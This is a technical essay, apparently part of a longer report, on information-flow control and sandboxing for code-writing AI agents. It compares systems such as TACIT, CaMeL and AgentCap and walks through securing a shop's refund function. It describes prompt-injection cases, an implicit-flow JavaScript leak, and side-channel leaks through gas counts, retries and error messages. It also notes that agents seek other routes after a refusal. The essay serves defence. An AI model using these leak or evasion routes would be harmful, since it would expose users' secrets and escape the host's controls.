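A system can also label the conversation. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) describes a small programming language for agents in which a conversation takes on the labels of everything a program adds to it. Anything the model writes afterwards carries those labels too. TACIT's criticism therefore applies to systems that track values only inside the interpreter, not to all run-time tracking.

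*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) notes that a label on a whole conversation can quickly become too restrictive. Once the conversation includes one delivery note, everything the model writes afterwards counts as untrusted. Garby and colleagues' language lets a program query the model in a temporary copy of the conversation and then discard the copy, which leaves the original conversation's label unchanged.

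### Checking before the run or during it

A run-time tracker sees only the steps that a program takes, and a secret can also leak through a step that it skips. Garby and colleagues found this flaw in CaMeL's interpreter. In JavaScript, with a customer's secret credit limit, the trick looks like this:

```
let high = true, low = true;
if (creditLimit > 5000) low = false;
if (low) high = false;
if (high) flag(id, "late");
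```

Suppose the tracker marks a variable as secret only when the program assigns to it under a secret condition. If the limit is above 5,000, `low` becomes false and secret. The program then skips the third line, so `high` stays true and unmarked, and the flag goes through. Otherwise, the program skips the assignment in the second line, so `low` stays true and unmarked. The third line then sets `high` to false without marking it, and no flag appears. The tracker detects no leak in either case, but the presence or absence of the flag reveals whether the limit is above 5,000. Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that their extended CaMeL has the same flaw.

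A compiler can examine both branches before the program runs. TACIT avoids the problem more simply by preventing code outside `map` from testing a classified value. Garby and colleagues keep run-time tracking but stop a program that tries to add to a public conversation while acting on a secret condition. They give a computer-checked proof that their language has a form of noninterference. In AgentDojo's banking tests, their agent resisted all but two of 1,296 attacks.

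The two methods can also work together. CaMeLoT, the system by Nikolaou and colleagues, adds a check before CaMeL runs a plan. It converts the plan into a map of all the orders in which its steps can happen, then searches the map for a path that breaks a rule. For example, if disconnecting a computer requires approval, a plan without the approval step fails before the agent starts a long investigation. The map treats a loop as if it could run any number of times, so the check sometimes rejects a safe plan. CaMeL's own policies still handle facts that emerge only during the run, such as who may read a particular file.

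### The effect on task performance

Odersky and colleagues report that models lose little or no performance when they write Scala instead of making tool calls. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer-service conversations for an airline and a shop, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT. On SWE-bench Lite, which contains 300 real software problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% with its usual tools. The difference of five problems could easily be chance. On τ²-bench, between 0.32% and 7.93% of programs needed a retry, depending on the model and domain, and those programs took 1.06 to 1.39 retries on average. Typical mistakes were forgetting that a value might be missing and mistyping dollar signs in text.

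These results don't show how protecting secrets affects task performance, because the airline and shop functions returned unwrapped data. LACUNA's larger losses on similar conversations also suggest that the effect of compiler-checked Scala on performance depends on the design. In the safety test, Sonnet completed 99.2% of the legitimate tasks when the secrets were wrapped and 83.3% when they weren't. MiniMax completed 90.0% and 88.3%, respectively. Sonnet's low score without the wrapper may be an artefact, since the model often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

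AgentDojo is a harder test because TACIT wrapped most of the benchmark's emails, transactions, messages and files. The table shows the share of tasks completed. CaMeL's figures come from its developers' earlier runs.

| Domain | TACIT, o4-mini-high | CaMeL, o4-mini-high | TACIT, Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL, Gemini 2.5 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 59.0% | 62.5% | 56.9% | 52.8% |
| Workspace | 52.9% | 81.4% | 50.5% | 53.8% |
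| Slack | 47.6% | 68.6% | 40.0% | 48.6% |
| Travel | 68.6% | 74.3% | 64.3% | 1.4% |

Odersky and colleagues call TACIT and CaMeL comparable. That is fair for Gemini, except that CaMeL failed nearly all the travel tasks. With o4-mini-high, TACIT did worse in all four domains. The gap was widest in the workspace domain, where nearly every function that reads emails, calendars or files returns wrapped data. The agent has to write code for text it will never see, which probably explains part of the gap.

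On AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks, Peters-Gill and colleagues found that CaMeL lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures occurred because CaMeL fixes the plan before the model sees any data, so the plan had no step for handling anything unexpected. The researchers also had to describe the format of every tool's results in advance, which Rai found necessary for agent-written code in general.

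CaMeL ran without any data policies in that test. Garby and colleagues report that turning on the policy checks halved the share of banking tasks it completed. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) reports that CaMeL by default refuses any tool call with untrusted data in its arguments, and that it completed 67% of AgentDojo's tasks under that rule. Plans are hardest to fix in advance for agents that operate a computer by looking at its screen. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) reports that a version of CaMeL for such agents kept at most 57% of leading models' performance.

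The order page is a favourable case. The fields are known in advance, and the late-orders loop never has to interpret text.

### Leaks and errors that remain

TACIT doesn't cover leaks through timing. A pure function can take longer if a secret begins with a certain letter, and an observer can measure the difference. Whether a program finishes can also reveal information about a secret. Most information-flow systems, including Garby and colleagues' language, allow this leak because preventing it would rule out too many useful programs. Leaking one bit per run does little harm unless the attacker can repeat the run. CaMeL's labels didn't cover the ordinary retry loop around its interpreter, so an attacker could use the loop to learn one bit about a secret per attempt, based on whether a call was refused.

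Gas metering makes this leak easier to exploit. A program can loop forever if a secret bit is one, and the host then reveals the bit by reporting to the model that the gas ran out. If the host also reports exactly how much of a 200,000-unit limit is left, each run could reveal up to 17 bits. If a program has handled secrets, the host should give the model the same short message whether the program succeeded, crashed or ran out of gas, and keep the details for the developers.

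Data can also leak through external commands. TACIT can limit which commands a program may start, but the Scala compiler has no control over a command once it is running. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only a short list of specific commands and running them in an ordinary sandbox.

Neither system prevents wrong actions that the rules permit. TACIT's guarantee explicitly excludes logical errors. With CaMeL, an attacker can't add a step to the plan but can influence which of the planned steps the program takes. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In one of their attacks, an advertisement imitated a cookie notice. The plan already included a step for closing cookie notices, so the agent clicked the advertisement and went to the attacker's website. On the order page, a customer could get the gift flag by writing that the order is a gift.

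These protections all depend on correct labels. TACIT wraps only files in directories listed as classified, so a key saved elsewhere arrives as plain text. Labelling too much also causes problems. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes label explosion, in which labels spread until every value carries all of them and the rules can no longer distinguish between values. Somebody then has to decide which data to release, and a mistake in that decision causes a leak that the system permits.

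### What a JavaScript host can do without such types

TypeScript's types don't record capabilities. JavaScript's `Proxy` can't carry labels either, because it wraps only objects, and strings or numbers lose any wrapper when a program combines them. Tracking every value would require a modified interpreter, but a host can get much of the protection by simpler means.

To answer the employee's question about repeat customers, the program only needs to know whether two orders have the same customer. The host can replace each email address with a random code, using the same code for all of a customer's orders and new codes for each run. The program can then compare the codes, but a leaked code is useless to the courier. Hashing the addresses, which scrambles each one in a fixed way, would be a poor substitute because anyone with a list of addresses could hash them and look for matches.

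If a program has to process the secret itself, the host can imitate `Classified.map` with a second interpreter. Odersky and colleagues mention that a language without capability types could use functions that can't hold any capabilities. A fresh interpreter with no proxies has that property:

```
const vault = new Map();

function mapSecret(id, source) {
  const box = newInterpreter({ gas: 50000 });   // no proxies
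  let result = "no result";
  try { result = box.run(source, vault.get(id)); } catch {}
  const newId = crypto.randomUUID();
  vault.set(newId, result);
  return newId;
}
```

The agent's program sends the function as text, such as `"e => e.split('@')[1]"` to get the part of an address after the @ sign. The program receives only an id for the result, but the host can show the result to the employee as plain text. Errors also produce an ordinary id, so they reveal nothing to the program. The host should charge the program a flat amount of gas for each call and always take the same time to reply. Otherwise, the gas charge or the delay would depend on the secret. As in TACIT, the program can't make decisions based on data it can't see.

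A coarser method needs only a switch in the host:

```
let hasReadNotes = false;

const readNote = (id) => {
  hasReadNotes = true;
  return String(store.get(id).note);
};

const safeFlag = (id, reason) => {
  if (hasReadNotes) throw new Error("no flags after reading notes");
  flag(id, reason);
};
```

*Language-Based Agent Control* describes a more refined form of this, in which an agent may use its tools until it reads untrusted data, after which the data's labels restrict which calls it can make. The switch accounts for skipped branches because it treats everything after the first read as dependent on the notes. It also protects against planted instructions, since a program that has read a note can no longer change anything. The switch has to stay on for later programs as long as the model's context contains any output from the notes. Many useful programs will fail under this rule, including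 one that flags gift orders. For those, the host needs to provide narrower functions, such as one that returns only whether a note contains a gift-wrap request.

The host can also run each program twice. It gives the first run invented email addresses and carries out the flags that run produces. It gives the second run the real addresses, ignores its flags, and shows its output only to the employee. The flags the host carries out can't reveal a real address, because the first run never had one. If a program's flags depend on the addresses, the two runs will produce different flags. The host can then warn the employee, but it shouldn't tell the model, because the warning would reveal something about the addresses. *The Attack and Defense Landscape of Agentic AI* (2026) lists this method, multiple execution, among the known methods of information-flow control and criticises its overhead, but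 the overhead is small for a ten-line script. At 80,000 units of gas, a second run of the late-orders filter would take less than a millisecond.

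## What the host application must build and maintain

A vendor can supply the interpreter, the gas counter and the proxy machinery, but not `readOrders` and `flag`. Those functions depend on what the shop's data means and what its staff want from the agent, so the order page's developers have to write them. They often can't give the agent the page's existing functions directly, because those depend on the rest of the page.

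Suppose the shop now wants the agent to prepare refunds for late orders. The page's `refund` function has worked well for employees because its button appears only on paid orders, turns grey after one click and opens a window asking for confirmation. The function itself checks none of this. Agent-written code calls the function directly, so it can refund an unpaid order, refund the same order twice, or pass an amount of minus €500.

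An operation for the sandbox has to be safe without the page's help. Let V be the set of acceptable states of the shop's data, in which, for example, no customer has received more money back than they paid. An operation is safe if, for every state s in V and every argument a:

op(s, a) ∈ V

A refused call changes nothing, so it meets the condition too. If every exposed operation meets it, no program can take the data out of V, because each call starts and ends in an acceptable state. Developers can then check the operations one at a time instead of considering every order in which code might call them.

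This reasoning assumes that calls don't overlap. If `refund` reads the amount already refunded, waits for the payment service and then saves the new amount, two simultaneous calls can both pass the check. The check and the change therefore have to happen in one step, such as a database transaction. The condition also doesn't cover leaks, so developers still have to look for dangerous combinations of operations.

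### Choosing what to expose

The first job is a list of the application's data, field by field, with a decision for each.

| Data | What the code gets | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Order id, status, days open | A copy | The late-orders task needs them |
| Total | A copy, in euros | The same |
| Amounts paid and refunded | Nothing | The host can check them itself |
| Name, email, address | Nothing | No current task needs them |
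| Delivery note | Nothing | Customers write it, so it can carry planted instructions |
| Session token | Nothing, ever | Anyone who copies it can act as the employee |

A new database column stays out of the sandbox until somebody adds it to the list. The list should also record who reads the output. Exposing an order's total is harmless if only employees see the flags, but not if the courier sees them too.

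### Writing the operations

Each operation has to be the right size. Piet, Chow and colleagues (2026), in *Position*, discuss this for agents that write a program before visiting a website. Operations as small as a click break when the page changes, while large ones can hide choices that matter. A single `checkout` function, for example, might silently choose the shipping and payment methods. On the order page, `setField` would be too small and `handleLateOrders` too large. For refunds, this function is about right:

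```
let calls = 0;
const proposals = new Map();

const proposeRefund = (id, cents) => {
  if (++calls > 20) throw new Error("too many refund calls");
  if (typeof id !== "string"
      || !Number.isSafeInteger(cents) || cents <= 0) {
    throw new Error("needs an order id and a positive number of cents");
  }
  const order = store.get(id);
  if (order?.shopId !== session.shopId
      || cents > order.paidCents - order.refundedCents) {
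    throw new Error("no refund of this size is possible");
  }
  proposals.set(id, cents);
};
```

The function only records proposals, like the version of `flag` that collects changes, and moves no money. A second proposal for the same order replaces the first, so proposals from repeated calls can't add up. The host supplies the shop's identity, as in the `Orders` binding. `Number.isSafeInteger` rejects fractions, infinities and NaN.

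If a check fails with an unexpected error, the call should fail too. Mellafe Zuvic's ScopeGate treats every such error as a refusal. The function above does the same, because an exception ends it before the last line.

The counter includes refused calls because they can reveal an order's refundable amount, which the list keeps out of the sandbox. The last error message shows whether the requested amount was too high, so a program can find the refundable amount of a €500 order in about 16 calls by halving the range each time. With a limit of 20 calls, a hostile program can find this amount for one order but not for all 2,000.

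### Setting the limits

An operation that handles money needs a limit on the total amount, in addition to the limits on gas, memory and calls. Twenty proposals of €500 can each pass the check and still add up to €10,000. In a similar example from *CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025), a rule that lets a browser agent check out carts under $50 doesn't stop it from checking out two carts at $49 each. The order page could refuse any proposal that brings the total for one request above €1,000.

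Test runs provide only the first figures for these limits. After release, the log will show which honest programs hit one.

### Asking a person before money moves

The employee can remove a flag but can't easily recover a refund, so the host should pay refunds only after the employee approves them. Approval helps only if the employee reads what they are approving. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of 290 reports about agents and users' files. In 80 of these, the agent's actions were approved automatically, which some users had chosen to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. Uninformative prompts contributed to 31, including some of the same 80. For example, a prompt to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it permits whatever the script contains.

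The order page should therefore show few prompts, and they should describe effects instead of code. After the program ends, one window can list all its proposals in lines such as "Refund €84.50 for order A-1042. You can't undo this." *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, recommends showing in the prompt whether an action is recoverable. Flags don't need a prompt. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), Anthropic reported that automatically approving actions inside a sandbox reduced prompts in Claude Code by 84%. The paper adds that this works only if the sandbox is configured correctly.

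An approval should cover only what the employee saw. *Agent libOS* (Zhang, 2026) describes a runtime that ties an approval to the exact arguments and checks them again before acting. If a colleague refunds A-1042 while the list is still on the screen, the host has to reject the second refund. The host also shouldn't turn ten approvals in a row into a standing permission. *Let the Agent Do It?* points out that they may reflect fatigue or deadline pressure instead of trust.

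The host must also handle what happens after a refusal, because agents typically look for another way when someone denies them permission. If the employee rejects an €80 refund, the agent might propose €40 instead, or flag the order with a note asking a colleague to refund it. The host can block further proposals for that order for the rest of the current request.

Rules written in advance reduce the number of prompts. However, *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026) cites an analysis of 21 proposals and five commercial agents, which found that such rules may not fit later situations. For example, an employee who allows refunds up to €50 during a delivery strike probably doesn't want that rule to apply after the strike ends.

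### Withdrawing access and keeping a log

When the program ends, the host discards the interpreter, which ends the program's access to `proposeRefund`. The host keeps the proposals longer, because the employee may not be available to review them right away. They should expire after about an hour, and the host should check at the time of payment that the employee still has the right to issue refunds.

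The log has to let someone reconstruct what happened without trusting the agent's account. *AGENTAO* (Jin, Jiao and Tong, 2026) describes a runtime for embedding agents in other applications. The runtime records the permission decision for every call the agent attempts, as well as the start and end of every call that runs. The order page's log could add the employee, the text of the program, the arguments and the reason for any refusal. *AGENTCAP* (Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, 2026) creates the decision and its log entry in the same branch of the code, so that a developer can't change one and forget the other.

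Separate log entries for start and end matter most after a crash. If the log shows that a refund started but not that it finished, the payment service may or may not have paid it. Zhang's runtime records each call to an outside service before making it. After a crash, it marks the outcome as unknown and doesn't repeat the call without checking. The order page can do the same, then use the refund's identifier to check its status with the payment service.

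### Describing the interface to the model

The order page now has a trap, because `total` is in euros and `proposeRefund` takes cents. A model that doesn't know this will propose a refund of €5 for a €500 order, and every check will pass. The description has to include the units and the effects:

```
/** Proposes a refund. An employee decides later; no money moves now.
 *  cents: whole cents, so 8450 means €84.50. At most 20 calls. */
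proposeRefund(id: string, cents: number): void
```

Using cents everywhere would be better still. Piet and colleagues found similar traps in the websites of WebArena, a benchmark for web agents. One shop's search required percent signs instead of spaces between words, and a forum's interface required a special header with every request. Poor tool descriptions are common. *From REST to MCP* (Mastouri, Ksontini and colleagues, 2025) cites a study of 856 descriptions, of which 97.1% had at least one flaw and 56% didn't clearly state the tool's purpose.

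### Reviewing every change

Changes elsewhere in the application can make the interface unsafe even if nobody edits the interface itself. Suppose the shop starts letting customers take part of a refund as store credit. If `refundedCents` counts only cash, `proposeRefund` will allow the shop to refund the same purchase twice. A new order status, a new reader of the flags or an engine upgrade also calls for a review.

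Automated tests can catch some of this. One test can compare the fields that `readOrders` returns with the approved list. Another can call every operation with random arguments in random order and check after each call that the data is still in V. The tests won't detect that the warehouse has started holding back flagged orders, so someone has to be responsible for the interface and be told about such changes.

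### How much work this takes

Odersky and colleagues report that the reusable part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines of code. The interfaces for the airline and shop in τ²-bench took a few hundred lines each, about as many as the tool descriptions they replaced. Only the reusable part, which developers write once, requires expertise in Scala's capability types.

These figures probably understate the work for an ordinary application. Both benchmark domains already had a set of tools, and the new interfaces copied their descriptions one for one, so someone had already decided what to expose and written the underlying code. If an application's rules are in the code for its buttons and forms, developers have to move them into functions first. The few hundred lines are mainly data types and function signatures, and don't include approval windows or a review after each release. Line counts also don't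 reflect the time needed to decide what the code should do. `proposeRefund` has only about 15 lines, but deciding what they should check requires someone who knows how the shop handles refunds.

### Who writes the interface

Companies already make these choices when they connect their services to agents. Mastouri and colleagues studied 116 official MCP servers. Where the company had published a machine-readable description of its service, the server exposed a median of 19% of the available operations. GitHub's service, for example, has more than 600 operations, while its MCP server has 51 tools. But 92% of the servers implemented their tools as bare wrappers, which pass the model's arguments on to the existing service, so exposing fewer operations doesn't narrow the ones that remain.

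Software can also generate the wrappers. In the same study, this worked for 76% of sampled tools, and for 94.2% after the software repaired errors in the service descriptions. These percentages don't measure whether a tool is safe to expose.

A model can also write the interface, which creates a new way to attack it. Piet and colleagues place the interface and its documentation in the trusted computing base and describe a possible attack in which a model explores a shop's website to write a function called `get_reviews`. One of the reviews contains planted instructions, and the model adds a line to the function that sends data to the attacker. Every later program that calls `get_reviews` leaks data, even if the model that wrote the program never saw a review.

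They propose three safeguards for generated interfaces. The model can work from source code, or from recordings made with test accounts, so that it never reads text written by outsiders. A program can check that each function makes only the requests its description declares. A person can review the code before anyone uses it. They consider doing this for many websites, and keeping up with changes to those sites, an open problem.

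Mellafe Zuvic goes further and rules out model output as a source of security policy, even for rules written before the agent runs. Odersky and colleagues accept an agent's drafts if a person reviews them. For the order page, a model could sensibly draft `proposeRefund` from the source code for a developer to review, while people set the €1,000 limit and decide which employees may approve refunds.

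### Applications that expose nothing

Sometimes the agent has to use an application that the host's developers can't change, such as a supplier's website. Few websites offer a programming interface that covers everything they can do. Piet and colleagues had six people judge the 860 tasks in the WebArena benchmark. They concluded that, with complete interfaces, programs written in advance could handle all of the tasks, 81% of them without calling a model at run time, but nobody ran those programs. The existing interface for the benchmark's forum offers only 16 operations, enough for 33% of the forum's 129 tasks.

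For such websites, Meng and colleagues built ceLLMate, a browser extension for agents that click and type like a person. Restricting the clicks themselves doesn't work well, since the same spot on the screen can open an email or delete it. In one experiment, they blocked an agent from navigating to a certain website, and it got there through a search engine. But to change anything on a website, the browser has to send a request, and a request has a definite meaning. The extension checks requests in four steps:

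1. The website's developers, or another trusted party, publish an "agent sitemap". It gives each kind of request a name, such as `PlaceOrder`.
2. They also write rules for these names, such as allowing `PlaceOrder` only up to a certain amount.
3. A model reads the user's task, but no web content, and selects the rules it needs. The user confirms them.
4. The extension intercepts each request, looks up its name and allows or blocks it.

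The ceLLMate extension blocked all 12 scripted attacks in a test on GitLab, a site for managing software projects. The scripts acted as an agent that an attacker fully controls. Every attack needed an action that the rules forbade, so the test confirms that the blocking works but not that the rules are good. On 209 tasks, three models selected exactly the right rules at least 94% of the time in every category, but some of the errors granted too much access. A series of page visits took 7.25% longer with 100 sitemap entries and 15% longer with 300.

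This approach gives up several protections that proxies provide. An agent allowed to open the supplier's page can see everything on it, because ceLLMate controls requests, not fields. It doesn't track where data goes or check the content of a permitted comment. It also can't interpret WebSockets, the continuous connections that many sites use for live updates. If a sitemap entry is missing or wrong, users have only the protection they have today. Some limits depend on values shown on the page, such as the cart's total, which may be out of date when the agent clicks.

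Someone still has to define the operations. The researchers wrote 51 sitemap entries for GitLab by hand, and each entry has to change when GitLab changes the request it describes.

### Fixed proxies, signed tokens or a full runtime

The order page sets in advance which proxies a program gets, and each proxy checks its own arguments. AgentCap and Agent libOS make more of the decision at the time of the call.

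AgentCap stands between an agent and its MCP tools. For each call, the agent states a purpose, and a policy engine checks seven conditions. If all seven hold, the engine issues a signed token for that one action, and a separate gateway verifies the token before making the call. In the sample policy for a bank, permission to send money lasts 30 seconds, covers one payment and requires the agent to already have permission to check the balance.

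The most useful of the seven conditions checks where an argument came from. The policy marks the employee's request as trusted and fields such as delivery notes as untrusted. AgentCap refuses a refund payment if the account number appears only in a delivery note, but can allow it if the employee also typed the number. The stated purpose gives weaker protection because the model supplies it.

Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo and on InjecAgent, another benchmark of planted instructions:

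| Benchmark and model | Successful attacks without AgentCap | With AgentCap | Drop in tasks completed when not under attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.63% | 5.09% | 3.1 points |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.23% | 0% | 7.2 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.24% | 8.63% | 11.7 points |
| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 11.95% | 0% | 5.9 points |

The researchers ran each test once and wrote the policies by hand after reading the benchmark's task descriptions. A real host can't read future requests, so it would probably block more legitimate calls. Some of the remaining attacks succeeded through arguments or fields that the policy should have marked but didn't, and others were meant only to change the agent's text. Each check took less than 0.2 milliseconds.

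AgentCap's trust scores fit agent-written code poorly. Each agent starts with a score of 0.8 by default, and AgentCap multiplies it by 0.7 after every refusal. After two refusals in a row the agent can no longer write, and after three it loses all its permissions. A faulty loop can trigger three refusals in a millisecond, so a host that adopts trust scores should count refusals per program, not per call.

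Agent libOS is for agents that run for days, write their own tools and start other agents. Every operation that touches a resource passes through one runtime. The runtime allows the operation only if there is a capability for it, enough budget remains, and any limit the host has set for the task permits it. Some operations also need a person's approval, but approval can't replace a missing capability. The runtime also labels data and checks who may receive it.

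The runtime completed all 33 of Zhang's scripted tasks, and none of the 119 effects it carried out was unauthorised. Three simpler designs, including one that asked for confirmation in a wrapper around each tool, passed the safety check in only 13 tasks. Zhang deliberately left parts of the runtime out of these designs, so they don't represent real products. All 12 runs with a live model were also safe and successful, including some that required the agent to issue one partial refund in a customer portal and ignore a planted instruction. The evidence from these runs is encouraging but thin, because Zhang tested one model and ran each kind of task only three times. Zhang also states that the runtime can't replace operating-system isolation or undo effects in outside services.

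I expect neither system to be worth the effort for the order page, since one employee's request leads to one short program with three proxies. The proxies don't need signatures, because the program can't forge a proxy or take it elsewhere. Tokens become useful when calls pass between several services or agents, and a full runtime becomes useful when an agent's tools and tasks keep changing. A host with fixed proxies can still use AgentCap's check on where an account number came from.

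### What users and developers give up

The interpreter contains the JavaScript language and little else. If an employee wants the late orders as an Excel file, the program can't download a library to create one. The host could bundle a library written entirely in JavaScript, which would use gas and memory, or offer an `exportSpreadsheet(rows)` operation. Libraries that need files, a network or compiled code won't run.

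Some requests also have to wait for a new release. An employee who asks for late orders by country will get nothing useful until a developer exposes the country field. The agent should report which field or operation is missing, and the host can log these reports so that developers know what to add next. Programs written before the data arrives can also fail when the data is unexpected, as CaMeL's plans can. In an example by Piet and colleagues, a search for the misspelled word "furnture" returns nothing and the program stops.

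A list of operations is the wrong approach for some work. A coding agent has to install packages, compile programs and run tests, and a data analyst may need Python with its scientific libraries. Wrapping each command wouldn't be enough, because commands can start other programs. Git, for example, can run programs named in a project's settings, so Zhang had to replace unrestricted use of Git with a fixed set of operations and turn off many of its features.

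Such tasks belong in a container or, for hostile code, a virtual machine. The host can still decide what goes in and comes out. For a sales forecast in Python, the order page's server could start a virtual machine without network access, copy in the four fields of each order, read back a single file of numbers, and then delete the machine.
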